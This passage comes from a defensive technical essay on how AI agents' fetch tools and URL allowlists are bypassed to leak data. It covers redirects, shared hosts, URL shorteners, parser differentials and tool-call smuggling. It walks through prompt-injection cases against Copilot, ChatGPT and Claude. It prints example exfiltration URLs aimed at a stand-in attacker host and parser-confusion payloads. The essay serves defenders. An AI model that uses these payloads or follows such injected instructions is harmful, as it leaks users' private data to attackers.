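In both attacks, the URL being checked contained the attacker's address. In SearchLeak, the address appeared in plain text after `imgurl=`, and the stolen title was changed only by replacing its spaces with underscores. A practitioner's blog post, trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, therefore recommends decoding every parameter, looking for addresses nested inside it and scanning the decoded values for sensitive data. It ranks searching for long random-looking strings much lower, since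 that search would not have caught SearchLeak's data.

Checking a URL for other addresses nested inside it would catch `https://docs.example/preview?url=https://attacker.example/log?code=4471`. The check is less reliable when the proxy accepts an address in an encoding that the check doesn't decode. It also can't tell harmless uses from harmful ones by the URL's form alone, because some legitimate services, such as image search, routinely receive outside addresses. Refusing nested addresses by default and listing exceptions is simpler, but it breaks some legitimate links.

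Logs are a poor safeguard against these attacks. Many companies set their monitoring to ignore traffic to approved hosts, which would have hidden both EchoLeak and SearchLeak. Browsers can report requests that break the security policy, but the request to Bing didn't break it. Bing's own request to the attacker came from Microsoft's machines, so the victim's company had no record of it.

Varonis classifies the Bing step as SSRF, but a block on private addresses would not have stopped it because Bing's request went to a public server.

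Open proxies pose a further risk to fetch tools because the tools read the reply. If an approved host such as docs.example has a translation or preview service that returns the text of any web page, the tool can read unapproved sites through it. An attacker can then feed the agent new instructions from attacker.example, and the tool will label them as content from docs.example.

### Shared hosts

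An attacker who can collect data through the approved site doesn't need the agent to send a request to another one. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* lists three conditions for this attack: the check must approve the site, the site must accept data in an ordinary GET request, and the attacker must be able to view what the site received.

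Microsoft's cloud gives each customer of its storage service an address under blob.core.windows.net, and customers can read the logs for their own storage. ChatGPT's url_safe check approved all of windows.net, including these addresses. A blogger opened a storage account and used a prompt injection to make ChatGPT display an image from it whose address contained the user's recent chat history. Microsoft's server received the data, and the blogger read it in the log. The same check approved apache.org, where the blogger could also inspect server logs.

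The blogger reported these bypasses to OpenAI in October 2024 and had not heard of a fix by the time the post appeared. The post recommends that OpenAI publish its list of approved domains so that outsiders can examine it, and let business customers set their own lists.

Claudy Day shows that sending data to an approved host helps an attacker only if the attacker can read it there. Claude's code sandbox could connect to only a few hosts, including Anthropic's own api.anthropic.com. Anyone can open an account there, so Luz put the key of an attacker's account into the hidden prompt. Luz's first idea was to have Claude send the stolen text to that account as a prompt, but this failed because Anthropic does not show account owners the text of prompts sent with their key. Instead, Claude uploaded the text as a file to the attacker's account through the Files API, a storage service on the same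 host. The attacker could then refer to the file in a new conversation and ask for its contents.

The sandbox's network rule approved the right host, and the data went only to Anthropic. But the rule did not check whose account would receive the data. Refusing any key other than the user's own would have closed this route without blocking the host.

An approved site can carry a message to an attacker through its download counts. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has a fetch tool called WebFetch, which normally needs the user's approval to open a new site. Some hosts were approved in advance, including huggingface.co, where anyone can publish AI models and data in their own repositories. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026), WebFetch opened every path on that host without a prompt, even if the user had restricted which tools Claude Code could use. Hugging Face counts a request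 for certain repository files as a download. An attacker could publish repositories, use a prompt injection to direct the agent to send a message by fetching files from some of them, and read that message from the download counts.

Counts give an attacker less information than a log because they don't record order. Suppose the attacker had ten repositories, one for each digit. If the agent sent the code 4471, the counter for 4 would rise by two and the counters for 7 and 1 by one each, leaving twelve possible codes. With ten repositories for each position, forty in all, the counts would identify the code exactly.

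None of the earlier defences detects this. A check on every hop passes because the tool contacts only huggingface.co, and a scan for secrets finds nothing because the addresses point to ordinary repository files and contain no private data. OpenAI's later exact-address match might well accept these addresses too, because a crawler could already have visited such public files.

The flaw affected Claude Code from version 0.2.54 until Anthropic fixed it in 2.1.163. GitLab's record rates its severity at 6.5 out of 10 and credits the report to the security company Novee. In Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* (2026), Novee researcher Elad Meged describes several rounds of findings against Claude Code, each of which Anthropic patched and paid for. From each patch he could see where the new boundary was, and so where to look next. He said the channel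 that survived to the last round had "no outbound connection to an attacker, no writes, no logs", which fits a download counter well.

### Would narrower path rules be enough?

An obvious reply is that the developers in these cases approved too much. If the list contained `docs.example/guides/` instead of docs.example, the agent could not open `/out`, `/preview` or `/mallory`. GitLab's record supports this reading, since it traces the Claude Code flaw to approval of a "bare hostname". A narrower rule would have helped in each case where the agent or its chat window sent the request:

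| Attack | The broad rule approved | A narrower rule | Would it have stopped the attack? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bing tracking links | bing.com | Leave out `/ck/a` | Yes, if Bing has no other redirector |
| EchoLeak | All Teams hosts | Only the paths for Copilot's own images | Yes, unless Copilot needs the preview service |
| SearchLeak | All Bing hosts | Leave out search by image | Yes, unless Copilot needs that feature |
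| ChatGPT and Azure storage | windows.net | Only known storage accounts | Yes |
| Claudy Day's upload | api.anthropic.com | Leave out the Files API | Yes, unless the sandbox needs uploads |
| Claude Code | huggingface.co | Only known publishers | Mostly |

Narrow rules have a good enough record that any developer who can write them should. They aren't sufficient, though, mainly because of the "unless" in several rows. A service is often approved because the product needs it. If Copilot has to show link previews, the preview service's path must stay approved, and the harmless and harmful requests then differ only in the address after `url=`, which a path rule doesn't check.

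Rules that exclude known bad paths work only if someone knows every bad path on a site that another company runs and can change without notice. Allowing only the paths the agent needs is safer, because a new redirector elsewhere on the site won't be allowed.

A Content Security Policy can include paths, but after a redirect the browser checks only the scheme, host and port against the policy. Suppose a policy approves images from `docs.example/img/` and `cdn.example/logos/`. If an address under `/img/` redirects to `cdn.example/mallory/pixel.png`, the browser loads the picture, even though it would block a direct request for it. The designers left the path out on purpose, as trackr.live explains, because a page could otherwise test one path after another to learn where another site redirects its visitors. That reason doesn't apply to a fetch tool that follows redirects itself, so the tool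 can check the full path at every hop.

Path rules also depend on the check and the server agreeing on what the path is. Dots and encoded slashes can make them disagree.

Ownership is a harder problem, and trackr.live argues that an approval must cover it along with host and path. On Azure storage, the customer's name is part of the host name, so a rule that matches whole hosts can tell customers apart. On Hugging Face, the publisher's name is in the path. On api.anthropic.com, customers share the same host and paths, and the key sent with the request determines the account, so a rule based only on URLs can't limit access to the user's own account.

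For those reasons, trackr.live recommends a list that records, besides host and path, who owns the resource, which operation the agent may perform, whether the address may contain another address, and whether the service is expected to fetch anything by itself. Filling in the list for a handful of services takes an afternoon. This isn't feasible for a general web-browsing agent, because nobody can fill it in for sites they haven't heard of.

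Allowing only carefully chosen publishers on Hugging Face still leaves a gap, because anyone can look up a public model's download count. An attacker could direct the agent to a trusted publisher's files and watch the counts for its downloads. Other people's downloads would hide the agent's on a popular model, but perhaps not on an obscure one. Closing the gap would require asking the user before each fetch or keeping private data out of any session that can reach the site.

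## What do URL shorteners change?

A URL shortener assigns a short address to a long one and redirects anyone who opens it. Bing's tracking links also lead to stored pages, but Bing decides what goes into its index. With a shortener, an attacker can choose the destination, often change it later, and see how many people have opened the link.

### How a short link works

In *Gone in Six Characters*, Georgiev and Shmatikov (2016) describe a shortener as an internal database that maps each short address to the original one. The short address ends in an identifier, usually made of lower-case letters, capitals and digits. Six such characters allow about 57 billion (62⁶) identifiers.

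Suppose a shortener runs at short.example.

1. An attacker submits the address `https://attacker.example/offer`.
2. The service picks an unused identifier, stores it in a table beside the long address, and returns `https://short.example/x7Kq2b`.
3. The attacker posts the short link in a comment on docs.example, and the model passes it to the fetch tool.
4. The tool sends `GET /x7Kq2b` to short.example. The service looks up the identifier, records the visit and replies:

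```
HTTP/1.1 301 Moved Permanently
Location: https://attacker.example/offer
```

5. The tool requests the new address, as it would after any redirect.

Bitly, one of the largest URL shorteners, returns a 301 redirect, while BL.INK returns a 307 by default, according to its *301 Permanent Redirect vs. 307 Temporary Redirect*. Links from free Bitly accounts now first open a page with an advertisement and a preview of the destination, according to Bitly's *Why are there ads on my links*. A plain networking library stops at that page.

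### What the short link hides

A person who reads a short link sees only the shortener's domain and an identifier. *Comprehensive List of User Deception Techniques in Emails* (2026) adds that people may be more neutral towards a shortener's domain than towards one they don't know. A model sees the same characters. It might treat `https://attacker.example/log` as suspicious, but an identifier like `x7Kq2b` gives no clue to the destination.

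A host allowlist checks only the host of a short link, such as short.example. If a developer has approved that host because customers often share short links, the check passes every link on it, whatever address the link leads to. If the tool follows redirects without checking them, approving a public shortener effectively approves the whole web.

Scammers use URL shorteners to hide where their links lead. *Read This Paper to Get $50 Million* (2026), a study of scam messages posted on Reddit, found widespread use of bit.ly and cutt.ly for this purpose. In *An Overview of 7726 User Reports* (2025), which covers scam texts that phone users reported, the most common shorteners were bit.ly and t.ly. Because many harmless links share those domains, the shortening service has to investigate and remove each bad link. Reputation databases are not a reliable substitute for this work. The Reddit study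 checked its links on VirusTotal, which collects verdicts from many antivirus engines. The engines often disagreed, and 14,651 of the 16,210 links from 2025 had never been analysed.

### Approved on Monday, changed on Tuesday

A short link's target is stored in the shortening service's table, so a check can't look for it in the link itself, as it usually can with an open redirect. The link's owner may also be able to change the target without changing the link.

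Some URL shorteners let users change where an existing short link leads. Bitly offers this on some paid plans and accepts the change as a single API request, so a script can make it. Short.io allows unlimited changes for free, according to *How to edit a destination original url*. Cuttly limits some plans to a new address on the same domain and lets others choose any address, according to *How to change the source URL in a short link?* Bitly doesn't allow changes to links that people made without an account, using a tool it has since discontinued. Rebrandly's *How to Edit a Custom Short Link* describes good uses for the feature, such as repairing dead links and pointing last year's event link to this year's event.

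Suppose the travel company's assistant keeps a list of links it has already checked.

- **Monday:** A stranger posts `https://short.example/x7Kq2b`, which leads to `https://docs.example/guides/baggage`. The tool looks up the destination, finds an approved host and adds the short link to its list.
- **Tuesday:** The stranger changes the destination to `https://attacker.example/baggage`. Another customer asks about baggage, and the model opens the same short link. The check finds it on the list, and short.example redirects the tool to attacker.example.

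The short link is identical on both days, so comparing it with Monday's copy shows nothing wrong. The model now reads a page that the stranger controls, which may contain further instructions. A user who clicked "always allow" on Monday has the same problem.

On Wednesday the stranger can change the link back, and anyone who investigates after that will find an ordinary baggage guide. Bitly shows the history of each link's destinations, with dates and clicks, in the link owner's account, so an outside investigator would need the company's help to see it.

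A 301 status code, which marks a redirect as permanent, doesn't guarantee that a short link's destination will stay the same. Bitly calls its 301 replies permanent because it does not modify shortened links, but its other help pages explain how customers can modify them. Both can be true if Bitly means only that it doesn't change links on its own initiative. A client may also store a 301 and skip the shortener next time. If a link's destination changes from docs.example on Monday to attacker.example on Tuesday, a link checker that stored Monday's reply will still resolve the link to docs.example, while a fetch tool that didn't store it will go to attacker.example.

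An exact-address match has a similar limit. Any web page can change its text after approval, but a short link can also start leading to a different site. If a crawler saw a short link on Monday, the link may still match on Tuesday, even if its destination has changed. The match still keeps private data out of the URL, but OpenAI says it doesn't guarantee trustworthy content.

### What the shortener and the last host learn

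A fixed short link doesn't carry the booking code, so the last host learns only that a request arrived. That changes if the model adds a query to the short link and the service passes it on:

| Service | What it does with `?code=4471` added to a short link |
|---|---|
| Short.io | Passes it on by default |
| Rebrandly | Passes it on for every branded link |
| Linkly | Passes it on and records it in traffic reports, if forwarding is enabled |
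| YOURLS, software for running one's own shortener | Drops it, unless a plugin is installed |

*Understanding and Managing Query String Parameter Merging in Short.io* gives an example in which a value in the short link overwrites a value of the same name in the destination. The link's owner can prevent the merging by adding a parameter to the destination address, but here the attacker owns the link. Rebrandly's *How do I pass URL parameters to the destination URL?* describes forwarding as a marketing convenience that lets a company label its links for visitor statistics. YOURLS strips the query by default, according to ecosyste.ms' *YOURLS Query String Forwarder Plugin*.

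If a URL shortener forwards query strings, an agent that follows an injected instruction to open `https://short.example/x7Kq2b?code=4471` sends the booking code to attacker.example. A rule that approves the short link's host and path would allow this request, but an exact-address match would reject it because of the query.

Both the shortener and the last host can receive the code. Linkly's *Forwarding URL Query String Parameters* says that the service records forwarded parameters in its own reports, so an attacker with a Linkly account could collect the code without running a server. The link could lead to a harmless page on docs.example, and a check of every hop would find only approved hosts if the shortener was approved. Visit counts can also leak the code if the attacker makes one short link per digit.

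Outsiders can also discover the addresses a shortener stores by guessing its short links. For their 2016 paper, Georgiev and Shmatikov queried Bitly for 100 million random six-character identifiers and got back 42,229,055 stored addresses. Some led to files in Microsoft's OneDrive storage that people had meant to share with only a few others, and about 7% of the accounts they found this way had a folder that anyone could write to. Short links to Google Maps revealed journeys between private homes and clinics.

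Google lengthened the identifiers in new map links to 11 or 12 characters in September 2015, within a week of the researchers' report. Microsoft told them that sharing by short link "appears by design", then removed the option from OneDrive in March 2016 but said the researchers' analysis had played no part. There are 62⁴ (nearly 15 million) times as many possible identifiers with ten characters as with six, so an attacker would need about 35 million guesses to find one valid link. An agent that can create short links should never shorten an address that contains a booking code, because this gives the code to the shortener and possibly to anyone who guesses the identifier.

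### Wrapped links

Many companies use mail-security products that rewrite the links in messages. When someone clicks a rewritten link, the request first goes to the security vendor, which blocks requests to known malicious sites and redirects the rest. Social networks also wrap links, as Twitter did with its t.co addresses.

Attackers have used these wrappers to disguise phishing links. Cloudflare's *Attackers abusing Proofpoint & Intermedia link wrapping to deliver phishing payloads* (2025) describes campaigns from June and July of that year in which attackers took over mail accounts at organisations that used Proofpoint or Intermedia, whose products then wrapped the attackers' links. In one example, a button in a fake Microsoft Teams message opened a short link, which led to a Proofpoint address and then, through more redirects, to a phishing page. The scanner blocks a site only if the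 vendor has already flagged it when the user clicks.

Cloudflare has a commercial interest in this finding because it sells its own mail-security product, but it published the addresses involved. It concluded that reputation-based URL filtering doesn't work against these links because the domains belong to trusted security companies. A host allowlist has the same weakness. Most outside links in a company's mail may begin with `urldefense.proofpoint.com`, which gives the developer of an assistant that reads that mail a strong reason to approve the host. The allowlist would then approve any address Proofpoint had wrapped.

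Some wrapped links are easier to check than short links because they contain the destination. In Cloudflare's Proofpoint examples, `http-3A__` stands for `http://`, so a check that only decodes standard URL encoding would miss the nested address. Code that handles Proofpoint's format can recover the destination without sending a request, then check it. If the destination is itself a short link, the tool still has to send a request to the shortener to find where it leads.

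### Refuse, expand or check every hop

A tool can refuse every shortener it knows without sending a request. A strict host allowlist does this automatically unless someone adds a shortener to it. A tool that may visit any public site needs a list of shorteners, and that list will be incomplete. Georgiev and Shmatikov wrote in 2016 that hundreds of shortening services had emerged, and found that Bitly also ran domains for other companies, including `1drv.ms` for OneDrive and `binged.it` for Bing Maps. Bitly's paying customers can also use their own domains for short links. Refusing short links blocks harmless ones too, though the model can often find the original page by searching.

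Another response is to expand the short link first and check the long address. Expanding it requires a request to the shortener, which records the visit and receives any query the model added. An expander that follows the whole chain also contacts attacker.example before the check can reject it. PromptArmor, a security company, warns that link previews in chat applications carry the same risk.

Expanding a short link can also give the wrong answer. According to the study of Reddit scam messages, services often treat antivirus scanners' requests differently from ordinary visits, so an expander may reach a different destination from the fetch tool. An expander can also stop too soon. SA Bugzilla's *Bug 8105* reports that the mail filter SpamAssassin didn't follow a short link that redirected to the same address with extra parameters. The reporter guessed that a safeguard against endless loops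 was the cause. The next redirect would have shown that the shortener had disabled the link.

If the tool expands a short link, approves the long address, and then requests the short link again, the link's owner may have changed the destination in between. The tool should instead request the long address it has just checked. If it also expands one redirect at a time and checks each address before contacting it, this is the same as the loop that checks every hop.

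| Response | What happens before the check sees the destination? | Does it catch Tuesday's change? | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Refuse known shorteners | No request goes out | Yes, if the list includes the service | Harmless links fail, and the list needs upkeep |
| Expand, check, then reopen the short link | The expander contacts the shortener and perhaps the last host | Only if the change came before the expansion | An extra request, and possibly a different answer |
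| Check every hop | The tool contacts the shortener | Yes | The tool must be allowed to contact the shortener |

Checking every hop is the best choice for tools that need short links. The developer can also restrict the tool to sending a shortener a GET request with a bare identifier and no query, accepting only a redirect in reply, and checking the new address as usual. An attacker who owns the link can still count visits, but can't collect a booking code from the query. For a tool with a strict allowlist and few short links to open, refusing them is simpler and also prevents visit counting.

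There is very little measured evidence on agents and shorteners. The closest study is *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026), in which a small open model, qwen2.5:7b, summarised malicious pages that it reached either directly or through up to three redirects. The model leaked data in 210 of 240 direct runs and 213 of 240 runs with redirects, which suggests that redirects don't make an injection less effective on that model. The study used no shorteners or URL checks, so it doesn't show how often a short link defeats a check.

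Lan and colleagues also tested a defence called "redirect detection", which stopped every leak in 30 runs. It blocked numeric network addresses, certain domain endings such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as "collect" or "steal", but it didn't follow redirects. In all 30 runs, the model reached the pages directly. A short link such as `https://short.example/x7Kq2b` would pass all of the defence's rules.

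## How can two programs read one URL differently?

Checking every hop works only if the check and the client identify the same host in each URL. Some checks get the host wrong because they compare text without parsing the URL. Others parse the URL by different rules than the client does. An attacker can exploit either fault without a redirect or a weakness in the approved site.

### Checks that only compare text

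Before version 1.0.111, Claude Code's WebFetch tool used `startsWith()`, which checks whether one text begins with another, to compare hosts with its list of trusted domains. NVD's *CVE-2026-24052 Detail*, an entry in the US government's database of security flaws, names modelcontextprotocol.io as one of those domains. An attacker could set up modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com, which begins with the trusted name, and the tool would have sent requests there without the user's consent. GitHub rated the flaw's severity at 7.1 out of 10. Users with automatic updates already had the fix when the record came out in February 2026, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-24052* (2026).

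The right end of a host name determines who controls it, although people read the name from left to right. A host name consists of labels separated by dots. Whoever owns `attacker.example` controls every name that ends in `.attacker.example` and can put any labels in front, so they can create `docs.example.attacker.example` for free and without anyone's permission.

Other text comparisons fail in similar ways:

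| Test | An address it wrongly accepts | Why |
|---|---|---|
| The host begins with `docs.example` | `https://docs.example.attacker.example/` | The owner of attacker.example chooses the labels in front |
| The host ends with `docs.example` | `https://mydocs.example/` | This is a separate domain that a stranger can register |
| The address contains `docs.example` | `https://attacker.example/?docs.example` | The text can appear in the path or query |
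| The host matches the pattern `help.docs.example` | `https://helpxdocs.example/` | In a regular expression (a search pattern for text), a plain dot matches any character |

The correct test compares whole labels. In Python, with `approved` in lower case:

```python
def host_matches(host, approved):
    host = host.lower().removesuffix(".")
    return host == approved or host.endswith("." + approved)
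```

The added dot makes the match start at the beginning of a label, so `help.docs.example` passes and `mydocs.example` fails. A developer who doesn't want to approve subdomains can delete the second condition.

A program can also check the host safely by testing whether the raw URL begins with `https://docs.example/`, including the final slash. Every parser should then read the host as docs.example, because the slash ends the host. This test rejects harmless variants such as `https://DOCS.example/`, and adding a path to the prefix isn't a safe way to restrict paths.

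### Two standards

`host_matches` needs a host, so a parser must first extract it from the URL, and parsers follow two different standards. RFC 3986 (Berners-Lee, 2005) is mainly a grammar that defines valid addresses but leaves programs a lot of freedom in handling invalid ones. The WHATWG URL Standard, which first appeared in 2012, is a procedure that reads an address character by character and repairs many mistakes. *yoU aRe a Liar* (Ajmani, Koishybayev and Kapravelos) reports that most browsers follow WHATWG and most other libraries and command-line tools follow RFC 3986, but that none of the programs examined follows either standard completely.

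RFC 3986 doesn't allow a backslash in a URL or treat it as a separator, but the WHATWG standard treats it as a forward slash in web addresses, so a browser opens `https:\\docs.example` as `https://docs.example`. Snyk's *URL confusion vulnerabilities in the wild* (2022) attributes this leniency to the many badly written links that browsers have had to handle. According to a comment in its source code, Chromium, the project behind Chrome, accepts any number of slashes before the host.

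A program's reading of a URL can also change from one version to the next. The developers of WebKit, the engine inside Apple's Safari, gave the example of a page on example.org that links to `https:/webkit.org`, which is missing a slash. Older versions opened webkit.org. Newer ones open `https://example.org/webkit.org`, as Chrome and Firefox do. A check and a client that agree today can therefore disagree after someone updates one of them.

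The table below gives an example URL for each common kind of parsing gap. No pair of programs has all of these gaps, and developers have fixed several.

| Feature | Address | What the check reads | What the client contacts | Why |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| User information | `http://x@attacker.example:80@docs.example/` | docs.example | attacker.example | The check takes the host after the last "@", the client after the first |
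| Backslash | `http://attacker.example:\@docs.example/` | docs.example | attacker.example | The check treats everything before "@" as a login, but the client ends the host before the backslash |
| Fragment | `http://attacker.example#@docs.example/` | docs.example | attacker.example | The check doesn't treat "#" as the end of the host |
| Percent-encoding | `http://%31%30.0.0.5/` | An unknown host name | 10.0.0.5 | The client decodes `%31%30` to "10" |
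| Unusual IP address | `http://167772165/` | An unknown host name | 10.0.0.5 | The number is the same address in another notation |
| Unicode | `http://baß.example/` | bass.example | xn--ba-hia.example | The programs use different rules for international names |
| Trailing dot | `http://attacker.example./` | A host missing from its blocklist | attacker.example | The final dot only marks the top of the DNS |
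| Dot segments | `https://docs.example/guides/../out` | A page under `/guides/` | `docs.example/out` | The client removes `guides/..` before sending the request |

A strict host allowlist makes the URLs in the rows with percent-encoding, an unusual IP address and a trailing dot harmless, because it refuses any host it doesn't recognise. These URLs defeat checks that block known bad hosts and let everything else through. The URLs in the first three rows are more dangerous for an agent with an allowlist, because the check reads an approved name.

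The row with two "@" signs comes from Tsai's *A New Era of SSRF*, a talk at the 2017 Black Hat security conference. curl contacted the first host in such an address, while the standard parsers in PHP, Go and Node.js identified the second as the host. The curl project fixed this in version 7.54. Tsai then got round the fix by adding a space, and the project declined to make further changes because curl "sort of assumes that you pass it correct input". That is a fair position for a tool that fetches addresses, but it means the URL check has to reject malformed ones by itself.

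An IPv4 address is a 32-bit number usually written in four parts, so 10.0.0.5 is the same address as 167,772,165 (10 × 256³ + 5). Many clients accept both forms. Tsai used an even shorter form, `http://0/`, to get past a list of blocked addresses in GitHub Enterprise, the version of GitHub that companies run themselves. On Linux, this address leads back to the machine itself. This bypass was the first of four flaws that together let Tsai run code on the server.

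International host names need a conversion, because the DNS traditionally carries only plain letters, digits and hyphens. Tsai showed that two older versions of the conversion rules turn the German letter ß into "ss", while the newest keeps it as a distinct letter in an encoded name that begins with `xn--`. The two resulting names can belong to different owners. Lemire (2025), in *How does your URL parser handle Unicode?*, replaced the last letter of microsoft.com with a Roman numeral that looks like an M. JavaScript converted it to the ordinary letter, as the WHATWG standard requires, but the standard libraries of Go, PHP, Python and C# returned the numeral unchanged.

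Ajmani and colleagues cite a 2021 report that a trailing dot on the host name bypassed the blocklist of Smokescreen, a dedicated security tool. Smokescreen is an egress proxy, a separate program through which all outgoing requests must pass.

Dot segments can defeat a check when a developer approves `docs.example/guides/` rather than the whole site. In a path, two dots mean "go up one level", so a check that tests only how the path begins will approve `/guides/../out`, which leads to the open redirect from the earlier example. Searching for two dots isn't enough, because a WHATWG parser treats `%2e%2e` the same way. Tsai found another way past this search in Node.js. The library kept only the last byte of each character, which turned a full-width letter N into a dot, so two of those letters passed the check and became "..".

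### How common are the gaps?

Tsai compared eight URL parsers with curl and marked five of the pairs as exploitable. One of Tsai's slides shows a single URL for which Python's own libraries and Requests connected to three different machines. WordPress, vBulletin and MyBB had the same weakness because they checked URLs with PHP's parser and normally fetched them with curl. Tsai found three ways to bypass the protection in WordPress.

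The security companies Claroty and Snyk published a joint study of URL parsers in January 2022. Claroty's *Exploiting URL Parsing Confusion* reports tests on 16 parsers and sorts the disagreements between them into five kinds: missing or malformed schemes, the wrong number of slashes, backslashes, percent-encoding, and URLs whose scheme the parser has no rules for. Snyk's account lists 15 parsers and omits the last kind. The companies also found eight vulnerabilities in software in use.

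One of the eight was in Clearance, a library that handles logins for websites written in Ruby. Clearance remembered the page a visitor had asked for and returned them there after login. If the visitor had followed a link to `/////attacker.example` on the site, Clearance stored that as a path. Its parser then removed two of the slashes, and the browser read the remaining three as the start of another site's address. This made the login page an open redirect, which Clearance's developers had tried to prevent.

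Claroty also describes a gap in Log4j, a Java logging library. In December 2021, attackers could make it load code from any server they named. A fix limited connections to an allowlist containing only the local machine, but someone soon bypassed it with a host of the form `127.0.0.1#.attacker.example`. The parser that checked the address stopped at "#" and read 127.0.0.1. Mainly on macOS, the parser that made the connection used the whole text as a host name, which the owner of attacker.example controls. Both parsers were part of the same lookup, so keeping the check and the request in one program doesn't guarantee that they read the address the same way.

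Reynolds, Bates and Bailey (2022), in *Equivocal URLs*, found thousands of differences between widely used parsers and reduced them to seven pitfalls. In the worst cases, clients with different parsers sent requests for the same URL to different hosts. The researchers used such URLs to evade VirusTotal and Google Safe Browsing, a list of dangerous sites that browsers check. Reynolds's dissertation, *URL location ambiguity* (2022), covers more than a dozen parsers and nine differences. If a developer checks a URL with a reputation service before the agent opens it, the service may evaluate a different host from the one the agent contacts.

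Ajmani and colleagues collected 1,445 addresses from the test suites of the parsers they studied and ran them through the other parsers. They found 4,262 inconsistencies among eight parsers, 56% of them in the scheme, host or port. One address had a line break inside the host 127.0.0.1, and it produced five different outcomes:

- Chrome's parser and the JavaScript library url-parse kept the line break.
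- Python's urllib3 and the JavaScript library uri-js encoded it.
- Python's urllib and the JavaScript library whatwg-url dropped it, which left 127.0.0.1.
- PHP replaced it with underscores.
- curl refused the address.

The total overstates the danger in ordinary browsing because test suites are full of deliberately awkward addresses. It also includes cases in which one parser refused an address that another accepted, and a refusal is usually the safe result. But the attacker chooses the address, so a rare gap is as useful to them as a common one if it exists between the two programs the agent uses.

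Developers can test their own pair of programs for such differences. *dippy_gram* (Kallus and Smith, 2023) automatically generates large numbers of URLs, feeds them to several Python parsers and compares the output. Earlier tools of this kind checked only whether the parsers reported an error, so they missed cases where both accepted a URL but extracted different hosts.

### Gaps in AI agents

Before version 0.4.0, AutoGPT, an open-source platform for building AI agents, checked URLs with Python's `urlparse` and then passed them to the Requests library. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-0454* (2025), a record kept by Spain's national cybersecurity institute, gives a URL that got past the check: `http://localhost:\@google.com/../`. `urlparse` treats everything before the "@" as a login and identifies google.com as the host. Requests uses a different parser, from urllib3, which ends the host before the backslash,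 so it connected to localhost, the machine running AutoGPT. This let users reach internal services through AutoGPT. The record rates the flaw's severity at 7.5 out of 10.

The short fetch tool in the section on redirects has the same pair of parsers in effect, because `urlsplit` and `urlparse` read hosts the same way. Suppose an injected comment makes the model pass the tool `http://attacker.example:\@docs.example/log?code=4471`. With affected versions of the libraries, `urlsplit` returns docs.example, which is on the allowlist, but Requests sends the booking code to attacker.example. The loop that checks every hop wouldn't help, because it uses the same parser.

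SecurityWeek's *Anthropic Silently Patches Claude Code Sandbox Bypass* reports that Claude Code's network sandbox, which is supposed to block connections to unapproved hosts, also had a flaw in how it handled host names. Anthropic told SecurityWeek that it had fixed the flaw in version 2.1.88 on 31 March 2026.

### The same fault in tool arguments

A fetch tool receives its URL inside a tool call, which models write in JSON, a common text format for structured data. A program may therefore parse the call before any program parses the URL. In many agents, one component (the guard) decides whether a call may run and another (the executor) runs it. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz (2026), in *Oops!... I Parsed It Again*, describe an attack they call tool-call smuggling, in which the guard approves one call but the executor reads the same bytes as a different call.

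Repeated keys are the simplest case. The JSON standard recommends that each name in an object appear only once but doesn't require it. Suppose a fetch call contains two values named `url`, first an address on docs.example and then one on attacker.example. A guard that keeps the first value approves docs.example, and an executor that keeps the last requests attacker.example. This can happen even if both programs parse URLs correctly.

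In the paper's main demonstration, the guard was written in Go and checked whether a customer owned the airline reservation they wanted to cancel.

1. An attacker who controlled a gateway on the call's route rewrote it to hold another customer's booking under `reservation_id` and the user's own under `Reservation_ID`.
2. Go's standard JSON decoder ignores the difference in capitals and keeps the last match. The guard saw the user's own booking and approved the call.
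3. The executor looked for the exact name, cancelled the other customer's booking and refunded $1,203.
4. The log recorded an approved cancellation of the user's own booking.

Of 55 pairs of parsers in current use, 43 disagreed on at least one call with a repeated or disguised key. In the same study, components produced different arguments or verdicts for 558 (11.9%) of 4,693 distinct schemas (the descriptions of a tool's arguments) collected from public tool servers. For 17 of these, the components disagreed about whether the schema was valid. For the other 541, they differed over default values, which some components fill in when the model leaves a field out and others don't. For example, if a fetch tool's schema sets `follow_redirects` to true by default and the model omits the field, a guard that doesn't fill in defaults checks the call without that setting, while the executor follows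 redirects.

A difference in any of these 558 schemas becomes an attack only if the guard's decision depends on the affected field and the attacker can deliver the bytes. In the reservation attack, the bytes came through the gateway, and an attacker there has a much stronger position than one who can only write a comment on a web page. None of the ten models tested put a repeated or disguised key into the call itself, even when a document told it to copy the text exactly. They did copy such keys into arguments that hold JSON as text, and in 82 of 84 calls a key with altered capitals then made a Python guard and a Go executor interpret the argument differently. An ordinary web page can therefore deliver the attack if the tool parses one of its arguments a second time.

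The paper's tests of defences apply directly to URLs. With no defence, 361 of 7,412 crafted inputs caused the attacker's action to run. Validating the call strictly against its schema reduced this to 352. Parsing the call once in the guard but forwarding the original bytes left it at 361, because the executor parsed those bytes again. Giving the executor the guard's parsed call, with only the approved schema's fields, stopped all of them, because the executor no longer had a second reading to act on. The researchers designed this defence themselves, so an independent test would be useful.

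### Parse once

The same fix works for URLs. The tool parses the URL once, checks the result, and gives the client that result instead of the original text. Tsai recommended in 2017 that programs reuse only the host name and IP address they had checked, not the input URL. Snyk advises systems with several components to parse a URL where it enters and pass the parsed request along. Daniel Stenberg, curl's author, stated the rule in the title of a 2022 post, *Don’t mix URL parsers*. Since 2018 curl's library has offered its own parser to other programs, so a tool that fetches with curl can check URLs with the same parser.

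In pseudocode:

```
function fetch(text):
    if text has a space, control character or backslash: refuse
    target = parse(text)
    if target has user information: refuse
    target.host = plain_form(target.host)
    if target.host has anything but letters, digits, hyphens, dots: refuse
    if target.host is a number not written as four decimal parts: refuse
    if not approved(target): refuse
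    return send(target)
```

`plain_form` converts an international name to its `xn--` form, and `send` uses the converted name. Refusing some URLs early makes the function less dependent on any parser being right. For example, the first line rejects `http://attacker.example:\@docs.example/` before it reaches the parser. With a path allowlist, the function should also refuse paths that contain dot segments or encoded slashes, because the web server has its own parser, which the tool's developer can't choose.

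Refusing odd addresses does little harm, because ordinary links rarely contain a login or a backslash, and the model can look for another source when a link fails. The rules above would also block IPv6 addresses, which have colons and brackets, but few public links use them directly.

In practice, `send` is the difficult step because many libraries accept only text. HTTPX lets the developer create a URL object, inspect its host and pass the same object to the client. With other libraries, the tool can build a new address from the checked parts, which must come from the same parse that the check used. Ajmani and colleagues give sample code that breaks this rule. One function approves an address with urllib3, and another takes the host from `urlparse`, then builds and fetches a well-formed address that leads to the wrong machine.

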